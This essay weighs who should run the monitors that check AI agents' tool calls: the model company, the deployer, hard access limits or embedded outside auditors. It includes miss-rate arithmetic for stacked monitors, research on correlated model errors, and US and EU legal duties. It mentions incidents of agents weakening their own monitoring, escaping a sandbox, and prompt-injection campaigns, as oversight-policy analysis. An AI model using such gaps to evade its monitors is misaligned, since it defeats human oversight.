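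In *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, which METR published in October, Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026) agreed, as their best guess, that the risk was low. They thought so mainly because of limits on what the models could do, and much less because of Anthropic's safeguards or alignment training. They called the report "far from adequate for confidently ruling out misalignment" and were not confident that its methods would detect a higher risk. Some examples that Anthropic had withheld from the public version led them to think that the company's monitoring was weaker than the public evidence suggested.

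The review was fairly light. Jurkovic and colleagues relied only on Anthropic's internal version of the report, so they couldn't test the monitoring themselves. Anthropic had the right to redact the review or veto its publication, but it made no redactions, and the reviewers changed none of their conclusions after its feedback. For its investigation of the four break-ins, METR has much wider access, including to transcripts from outside the period of the incidents and to employees who may share confidential information.

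If the reviewers are right about why the risk was low, the August rating is weak evidence about the risk from Anthropic's next, more capable models. The limits on the models' abilities that reassured METR will weaken as the models improve, and the monitoring would have to prevent harm that current models can't cause.

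## Who should run the monitor

METR's doubts about Anthropic's monitoring leave customers with four options. They can rely on the monitor that comes with the agent, run their own, restrict the agent so tightly that monitoring matters less, or press for outsiders to inspect the model company. Each option has serious advocates, though most of them also have commercial interests.

### Nadella's case for the deployer

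Microsoft's chief executive argued for control by deployers in *Models as Insider Risks in the Super Intelligence Era* (Nadella, October 2026). He begins by saying that engineers can trace a fault in ordinary software to a particular piece of code, but can't trace a model's behaviour to particular training data or numbers inside the model. Companies nevertheless give these models sensitive data and let them take important actions. Nadella argues that a model company's assurances don't relieve the deployer of responsibility for the results.

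The proposed remedy is to treat a model as an insider risk, security staff's term for a person whose access means that a mistake or betrayal could do serious harm. Companies already manage such people by establishing who they are, limiting what they can reach, logging what they do and setting boundaries. This doesn't assume malice, since any capable actor with access can make a mistake or fall under an attacker's control. Nadella wants to "separate the supply of intelligence from the authority over it", so that the deployer, rather than the company supplying the model, decides what it may do.

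Under this argument, even a deployer that fully trusts its model has reason to limit the model's access, just as banks limit the access of honest employees. Nadella also cites a security principle from the 1970s, that a program must not be able to bypass or tamper with whatever enforces its permissions. OpenAI's agents could weaken their own monitoring in October because OpenAI's systems didn't meet that standard.

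The comparison with employees probably understates the danger, because five hundred copies of one agent may all make the same mistake at about the same time, which five hundred employees are unlikely to do.

Nadella's essay supports controls outside the model more clearly than it supports buying a second AI classifier. It warns of "nested black boxes", in which an opaque model runs inside an opaque harness while another opaque model monitors it. A deployer that adds a supplier's language model as a monitor could create this arrangement. Nadella proposes surrounding models with fixed rules and human controls, and keeping records that let people reconstruct an outcome without relying on the model's own account.

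Some of what the essay asks for can come only from the model company. Nadella calls a visible chain of thought non-negotiable, though not sufficient, because nobody yet knows how to make a model's outputs consistently faithful. He also wants the people affected to be told promptly when a system fails. A deployer can insist on both when it chooses a supplier.

Cost is a fair objection, because a bank can pay people to write rules, label cases and retest a monitor after every update, but a firm of ten people can't. The small firm can still use its own knowledge to decide which systems the agent may reach, remove the agent's other permissions and keep a separate copy of the logs. It could then let the monitor built into the product check individual calls.

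### The monitor that people already have

Anthropic and OpenAI can argue that many users skip a safer option when it takes effort, and that a monitor that is on by default reaches those users with no effort on their part. According to Anthropic, 62% of Claude Code's users had either run it with permission checks off or clicked "don't ask again" for a shell command. Garner Health, one of Anthropic's customers, used central settings to make auto mode the default for all 550 of its employees. In August, Anthropic also stopped charging users on its individual and team subscriptions for the computing the classifier uses.

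OpenAI makes a similar case. Trębacz and colleagues report that sessions with Auto-review stop for human approval about 200 times less often than sessions with manual approval. By the end of April, most use of the Codex desktop app inside OpenAI, measured by text processed, ran with Auto-review, so a monitor that a company plans to build next year can't compete with it.

The model company can also fix its monitor for all its customers at once. When Apollo found weaknesses in auto mode, Anthropic's changes reached even customers who didn't know about the test. A deployer with its own monitor would have to find someone to attack the monitor and then fix the faults itself. However, a bad update from the model company also reaches every customer.

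Anthropic has shown that people use its monitor, but not that it is better than a good independent one. Its published tests compared auto mode with human approval and with Codex, but not with a monitor that a deployer had built around its own records and rules. Anthropic also reports that business users who adopted auto mode propose about 25% more code changes. That figure measures output rather than safety, and it may partly reflect differences between the users who adopted auto mode and those who didn't.

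Neither company claims its monitor is sufficient for everything. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. Trębacz and colleagues at OpenAI write that agents should one day have the same permissions as employees, but that this is not yet possible. For now they would give an agent less access than an employee, which is more cautious than the insider comparison suggests.

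### What a second monitor adds

A deployer can leave the built-in monitor on and add its own, so that a call runs only if both allow it. The built-in monitor might miss 17% of dangerous calls, as auto mode did in March on Anthropic's examples of overeager agent actions, and the deployer's might miss 10%, roughly Auto-review's rate on OpenAI's synthetic dangerous calls.

The built-in monitor misses 17% of dangerous calls. If the two monitors' errors are unrelated, the deployer's monitor misses 10% of those, so 1.7% of dangerous calls get past both (17% × 10%). If the deployer's monitor instead misses half of what the built-in one misses, 8.5% get past both (17% × 50%).

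| Monitors in use | Dangerous calls that get through | Chance that at least one of ten gets through |
|---|---|---|
| Built-in monitor alone | 17% | 84% |
| Deployer's monitor alone | 10% | 65% |
| Both, with unrelated errors | 1.7% | 16% |
| Both, with heavy overlap | 8.5% | 59% |

The last column is calculated as if the ten calls were independent, which real calls rarely are. Even so, the table shows why the number of monitors is a poor guide to safety. With heavy overlap, the pair does only slightly better than the deployer's monitor alone, because the built-in monitor also misses 85% of the calls that the deployer's monitor misses.

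False alarms add up as well, since a harmless call now has to get past both monitors. Suppose the built-in monitor blocks 0.4% of harmless calls and the deployer's blocks 1%. In 10,000 calls, ten of them dangerous, the built-in monitor would block about 40 harmless ones, and the deployer's could block as many as 100 more. The deployer's monitor would also stop about 1.5 dangerous calls that the built-in one had missed, or about 0.85 if the two tend to miss the same calls.

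That works out to up to 65 needless blocks for each extra dangerous call stopped, or nearly 120 if the two monitors' errors overlap heavily. By a similar estimate, the figure for running auto mode with only its fast filter would be about 780. A second monitor can therefore be worth adding even when its errors overlap heavily with the first one's. The deployer could reduce false alarms further by using the second monitor only for calls that touch important systems. If those were 5% of all calls, it would add about five false alarms instead of 100, but dangerous calls elsewhere would get only one check.

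Anthropic's study with paid testers measured overlap, though between a classifier and people. Auto mode missed 116 of the 1,053 planted commands, and the testers caught only six of those. Together they would have stopped 943 commands (89.6%), compared with 937 (89.0%) for auto mode alone.

The testers' low catch rate explains most but not all of this. They caught 13.6% of the commands overall, so they would have caught about 16 of the 116 if their errors had been unrelated to the classifier's. They caught 14.6% of the commands that auto mode blocked (137 of 937). Commands that looked acceptable to the classifier probably tended to look acceptable to people too. The numbers are small, and the study doesn't measure how much two AI monitors' errors would overlap.

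### Whether models share blind spots

Research gives good reason to expect different language models to make some of the same mistakes. In *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025), Kim, Garg and colleagues compared the errors of more than 350 models. On one public leaderboard, when two models both got a question wrong, they gave the same wrong answer 60% of the time. Models that shared a developer or an underlying design made more similar errors, which supports buying a monitor from a different company. But the larger and more accurate models made highly correlated errors even when different companies had built them.

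Goel, Strüber and colleagues (2025) found in *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight* that models' mistakes become more alike as the models become more capable. They also found that models grading other models' answers favoured models similar to themselves. If that carries over to monitoring, a monitor might be too lenient towards an agent from its own model family, because the agent's reasons would look familiar.

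Neither study tested monitors of tool calls. The closest evidence comes from *CyberDual*, in which two Claude models tended to miss the same planted flaws in software. The calculation above requires the rate at which one monitor fails when the other has failed. The 60% figure can't be used for this, because it describes which wrong answer the models gave when both had failed. Two monitors that wrongly allow a call always give the same wrong answer.

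A deployer can measure how many of the built-in monitor's misses its own monitor also misses by running both on the same planted calls. If the built-in monitor misses 20 calls and the deployer's catches 12 of those, both miss the other eight, an overlap of 40%. The 95% confidence interval would run from about 19% to 64%, so 20 misses give only a rough estimate. At a miss rate of 17%, collecting 20 misses would take about 120 planted calls.

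Switching the monitor to another company's model won't help if neither model has the fact needed to spot a mistake, such as who owns the job an agent is about to cancel. A monitor with access to the list of owners could catch the mistake even if it used the same model as the agent. For overeager actions, giving the monitor different information may matter more than using a different model, though nobody seems to have compared the two.

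### Limits that hold whatever the model decides

Simon Willison, the software developer who questioned auto mode's zero result, has long argued for removing dangerous combinations of access. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025), he warns that an attacker can steal data through an agent that has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to send information out. He advises against ever combining all three. He is sceptical of products that advertise catching 95% of attacks, because an attacker can keep trying until one gets through.

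Nadella's call for fixed rules around the model supports the same conclusion. Hard limits are especially attractive for stopping attackers and misaligned models, because both may disguise what they do.

But people have to set the limits correctly. Anthropic concluded that before its July incidents it had relied largely on one layer of defence, the configuration of the test environment. When the configuration was wrong, nothing else prevented the incidents. A correct configuration can also fail, as when OpenAI's models used an unknown vulnerability to escape a sealed sandbox.

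Anthropic's new practices for outside testers include a check that deployers could copy. Before an evaluation, the tester has the model look for weaknesses in the sandbox's configuration and then try to escape, telling it to stop and report if it succeeds. People closely supervise the exercise, which runs without an internet connection and ideally inside a second sandbox. Anthropic also wants limits phrased as instructions, such as "You should not access the internet", because a claim that the model has no access may turn out to be false.

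Hard limits also take more work than their advocates sometimes admit. Anthropic moved roughly 150 product engineers to security, reliability and privacy work in the spring, and its product teams paused most new features. Among other changes, it blocked outgoing traffic from its computing clusters by default and reduced the number of accounts with standing access to customer data.

Many useful agents need all three of the abilities on Willison's list. An office assistant that reads incoming mail, searches company documents and sends replies would be much less useful if any one of them were removed. Limits, such as allowing replies only to addresses already in the conversation, can reduce how many actions need judgement, but someone or something still has to judge whether an attachment belongs in the reply.

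### What each party knows

The model company and the deployer can each notice things that the other can't. The company can read reasoning that many customers never receive, and it can compare activity across customers. Suppose an attacker plants the same hidden instruction on many websites, and one agent session in 100,000 encounters it. A deployer with 10,000 sessions a month would probably never see it. A company with 100 million sessions would have about 1,000 examples, enough to recognise a campaign and warn the affected customers.

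The deployer knows which database is live, which client has forbidden cloud storage and who left the company yesterday. A central monitor can use such facts only if the deployer supplies them and keeps them current.

In its rules for outside testers, Anthropic asks the evaluator to run a monitor that has been given the permitted scope, because the evaluator knows what the exercise permits. The rules apply to unusually risky tests, and customers who use models with the normal safeguards are exempt. But the same reason applies to any deployer that sets limits the model company can't know.

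The model company and the deployer could share conclusions without sharing all the information behind them. The company could tell the deployer that an agent's reasoning had triggered an alarm without releasing the full reasoning, and the deployer could tell the built-in monitor that a file is restricted without sending the file. Claude Code's hooks already let a deployer attach facts to a tool's result. A warning from the company to the deployer would be just as useful, particularly if it arrived before the agent's next tool call ran.

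### Incentives and privacy

A model company loses customers if its monitor interrupts them too often, but when the monitor misses a dangerous call, the customer usually suffers first. The company therefore has some reason to tolerate misses. A similar pressure led the developer of Mythos 5 to release the more convenient version of the model. But a widely reported failure can hurt a company's business with every customer, not just the one affected.

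Deployers have a direct interest in protecting their own systems, but a manager who controls the monitor can weaken it when it delays a release. Deployers also have less reason to care about harm to strangers, such as a person their agent falsely accuses in an email. An independent monitor therefore needs protection from the deployer's staff as well as from the model company. At a minimum, the team whose agent gets blocked shouldn't be able to change the rules alone.

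Privacy gives deployers another reason to run the monitor themselves. ITPro's *A company should be able to use a model* reports that Microsoft CEO Satya Nadella argued in July that companies are "paying twice" for AI, because model companies also gain access to their customers' proprietary data. Nolan (2026), in *Big Tech's top executives warn enterprises are giving away too much*, reports that several other executives and investors had raised concerns about this access. Microsoft benefits if customers share these concerns, but they could still be reasonable.

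How much more data a monitor exposes depends on who runs it and how they use the data. If the agent's model runs on the model company's servers, the company already receives the tool calls, so checking them there immediately discloses little more. Keeping records for later review, or searching them for patterns across customers, discloses more. Using an outside supplier's monitor gives the same data to another company. A deployer that runs the monitor on its own machines discloses the least additional data, but it loses warnings based on other customers' experience.

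### Open-weight models and malicious customers

When a deployer runs an open-weight model on its own computers, the developer doesn't see the tool calls and can't suspend the deployer's account or fix a monitor remotely. Nadella's essay applies the insider approach to both open-weight and closed models, but the deployer's role matters more with open-weight models because no model company is watching. A cloud provider that hosts the model might do some monitoring, and the customer should find out whether it does.

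In exchange, the deployer of an open-weight model can read everything the model writes, including its reasoning, so it can run the separate reasoning check that many customers of closed models can't. It can also keep the model and the monitor unchanged until it has tested a new version. An organisation with skilled staff can use these advantages, but one without such staff may end up running an agent with no monitor.

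Malicious customers are the strongest reason to keep model companies involved. A criminal who uses an agent to break into other people's systems won't install a monitor, or will write rules that allow the break-ins. Anthropic's classifiers for prohibited hacking don't depend on the customer's cooperation. If model companies left monitoring to their customers, this protection would disappear.

An honest company is mainly responsible for catching its own malicious employees, since the model company's terms might not forbid what they ask for. So deployers have to watch for malicious users, and the model company has to watch for malicious deployers.

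Some customers who do legitimate security work get models with fewer safeguards. Anthropic says it is developing practices for partners that use Mythos 5, which runs without its hacking safeguards. Those partners will presumably have to do more monitoring themselves, and Anthropic will have to check that they do. If a criminal runs an open-weight model on private hardware, neither form of monitoring applies, and the main protection left is the defences of the systems under attack.

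### Outside auditors

An auditor can't stop a tool call, but it can check whether a company's monitoring works as the company claims. Apollo Research's *Embedded Evaluators are necessary for meaningful external testing* (2026) argues that tests of a finished model come too late, because some of the worst risks may arise while a company uses the model internally, long before release. Many risks also depend partly on the company's procedures. Such a test wouldn't show whether the monitors covered every internal agent or what staff did after an alert.

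Apollo therefore wants embedded evaluators, outsiders with the same access as employees. GovAI's *Embedded Assessments for Frontier AI* recommends that these evaluators assess at least the monitoring of internal agents, the security controls and permissions around them, and the alignment of the models. It also recommends continuous assessment, with detailed public reports at least every three months and a clear way to escalate urgent findings. Such access can reveal gaps in a company's monitoring, as when METR discovered that OpenAI's covered only part of its strongest agents' traffic.

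Companies granted more access during 2026. For METR's *Frontier Risk Report (February to March 2026)*, Anthropic, Google, Meta and OpenAI each gave METR access to their most capable internal models, including the raw chain of thought, and shared private information about how they monitored their agents. The companies decided which non-public information METR could publish. In October, Anthropic's *An update on independent evaluators* (2026) announced employee-like access for a METR team. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Gives Six METR Employees Access to Internal AI Tools* (2026) reports that six METR employees received company equipment and workspace, and that Anthropic can still require some redactions.

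On 14 October, METR set out a proposal to make companies' redactions visible. A company may remove non-public information, but METR keeps the right to disclose the removal and whether any finding depends significantly on the missing material. This is better than the veto Anthropic held over the review by Jurkovic and colleagues.

METR's *Independent Assessment of AI R&D Acceleration at Anthropic in October 2026* (2026) was an early, difficult test of the new terms. It examined how much AI was speeding up Anthropic's research. METR could freely share its highest-level conclusions about risk, but Anthropic redacted most of the evidence METR had found most informative in reaching those conclusions. Anthropic said it wanted to remove confidential information that could help other AI developers move faster. METR published a table of the important evidence it could and couldn't discuss, so readers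 know roughly what is missing, but they still have to trust METR's interpretation of the redacted evidence.

In *Evidence about risk should be transparent*, Cotra (2026) warns against this kind of reliance. Cotra, who also helped investigate the Hugging Face break-in, argues that the science is not yet developed enough to justify talk of "auditing". There are no settled methods for measuring whether powerful AI systems might try to undermine human control, and companies rarely make standard claims that an auditor could verify. Good scores on alignment tests may mean only that training taught the model to do well on those tests.

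That is a serious objection to certifying that a model is safe, but a weaker one to auditing a monitor. An auditor can measure how much agent traffic reaches the monitor, plant dangerous calls and time the response to an alert. Apollo Research's *Principles for Embedded Evaluations* (2026) proposes that developers state their safety claims and evaluators try to verify or falsify them. A suitable claim would be "Our monitor checks at least 99% of internal agent traffic." Apollo adds that this may achieve little if evaluators lack access or resources, or if companies ignore the findings when making decisions.

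On 16 November, OpenAI signed agreements with four assessors, including METR, Apollo and the interpretability company Goodfire. Mowshowitz (2026), in *OpenAI Somewhat Embeds Good Evaluators*, praises the choice of partners but argues that the agreements fall short of the employee-level access that OpenAI's chief executive, Sam Altman, pledged in September. OpenAI presents the agreements as meeting a different pledge, which companies made in the White House Accord, to work with independent auditors or evaluators.

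Anthropic says that evaluators should hold no equity in the company they assess and shouldn't depend on it financially or operationally. An evaluator can also have a less direct commercial interest. Apollo, for example, sells a monitor, so it could end up assessing a rival to its own product. These assessments also concentrate on how companies handle their own agents, so a deployer such as a hospital is unlikely to learn from them how often the built-in monitor would miss a dangerous change to its patient records.

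### What the law asks of each party

The EU's AI Act places duties on deployers as well as model companies. Organisations that deploy systems the Act classes as high-risk, such as those that screen job applicants or assess creditworthiness, must follow the supplier's instructions and assign competent people to oversee the system. They must also monitor how it operates, report serious incidents and keep the logs under their control for at least six months. The supplier must design the system so a person can interrupt it, which resembles Nadella's emergency brake. An ordinary coding agent would usually fall outside the high-risk category.

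These deployer duties were originally due to apply from 2 August 2026. The European Commission's November 2025 plan to simplify the Act moves that date to December 2027 for the uses the Act lists and to August 2028 for AI built into regulated products. Deployers should confirm which date applies to their system.

In the United States, the main state laws on frontier AI regulate the developers. The Paypers (2026), in *New York RAISE Act*, and Morrison Foerster (2026), in *Illinois Raises the Bar on Frontier AI*, describe their terms:

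| Law | Main duties of large frontier developers | When |
|---|---|---|
| California, SB 53 | Publish a safety framework, protect whistleblowers and report critical safety incidents within 15 days | In force since January 2026 |
| New York, RAISE Act | Publish a safety framework and report critical safety incidents within 72 hours | From 1 January 2027 |
| Illinois, SB 315 | Undergo an independent audit every year | Law takes effect at the start of 2027, audits begin in 2028 |

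New York's requirements apply to developers with more than $500 million in annual revenue, and the penalty for a first violation can reach $1 million. Illinois is the first state to require annual independent audits, which would give outside assessments a legal basis that company pledges lack.

Internal use is harder to regulate because it starts before the public knows that a model exists. *Risk Reporting for Developers' Internal AI Model Use*, by Maheshwari, O'Brien and colleagues, notes that companies use their most advanced models internally for weeks or months before releasing them. Anthropic had Mythos Preview available internally for at least six weeks before announcing it. California's law partly addresses this gap by requiring large developers to send state officials summaries of their assessments of catastrophic risk from internal use.

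The reporting duties leave out most of what a deployer would want to know. California uses the term "critical safety incident" only for grave events, such as a loss of control over a model that kills or injures someone. Neither an agent deleting one customer's database nor an update that makes the built-in monitor miss dangerous calls more often would normally qualify. A deployer that wants notice of these events has to negotiate for it in its contract with the model company.
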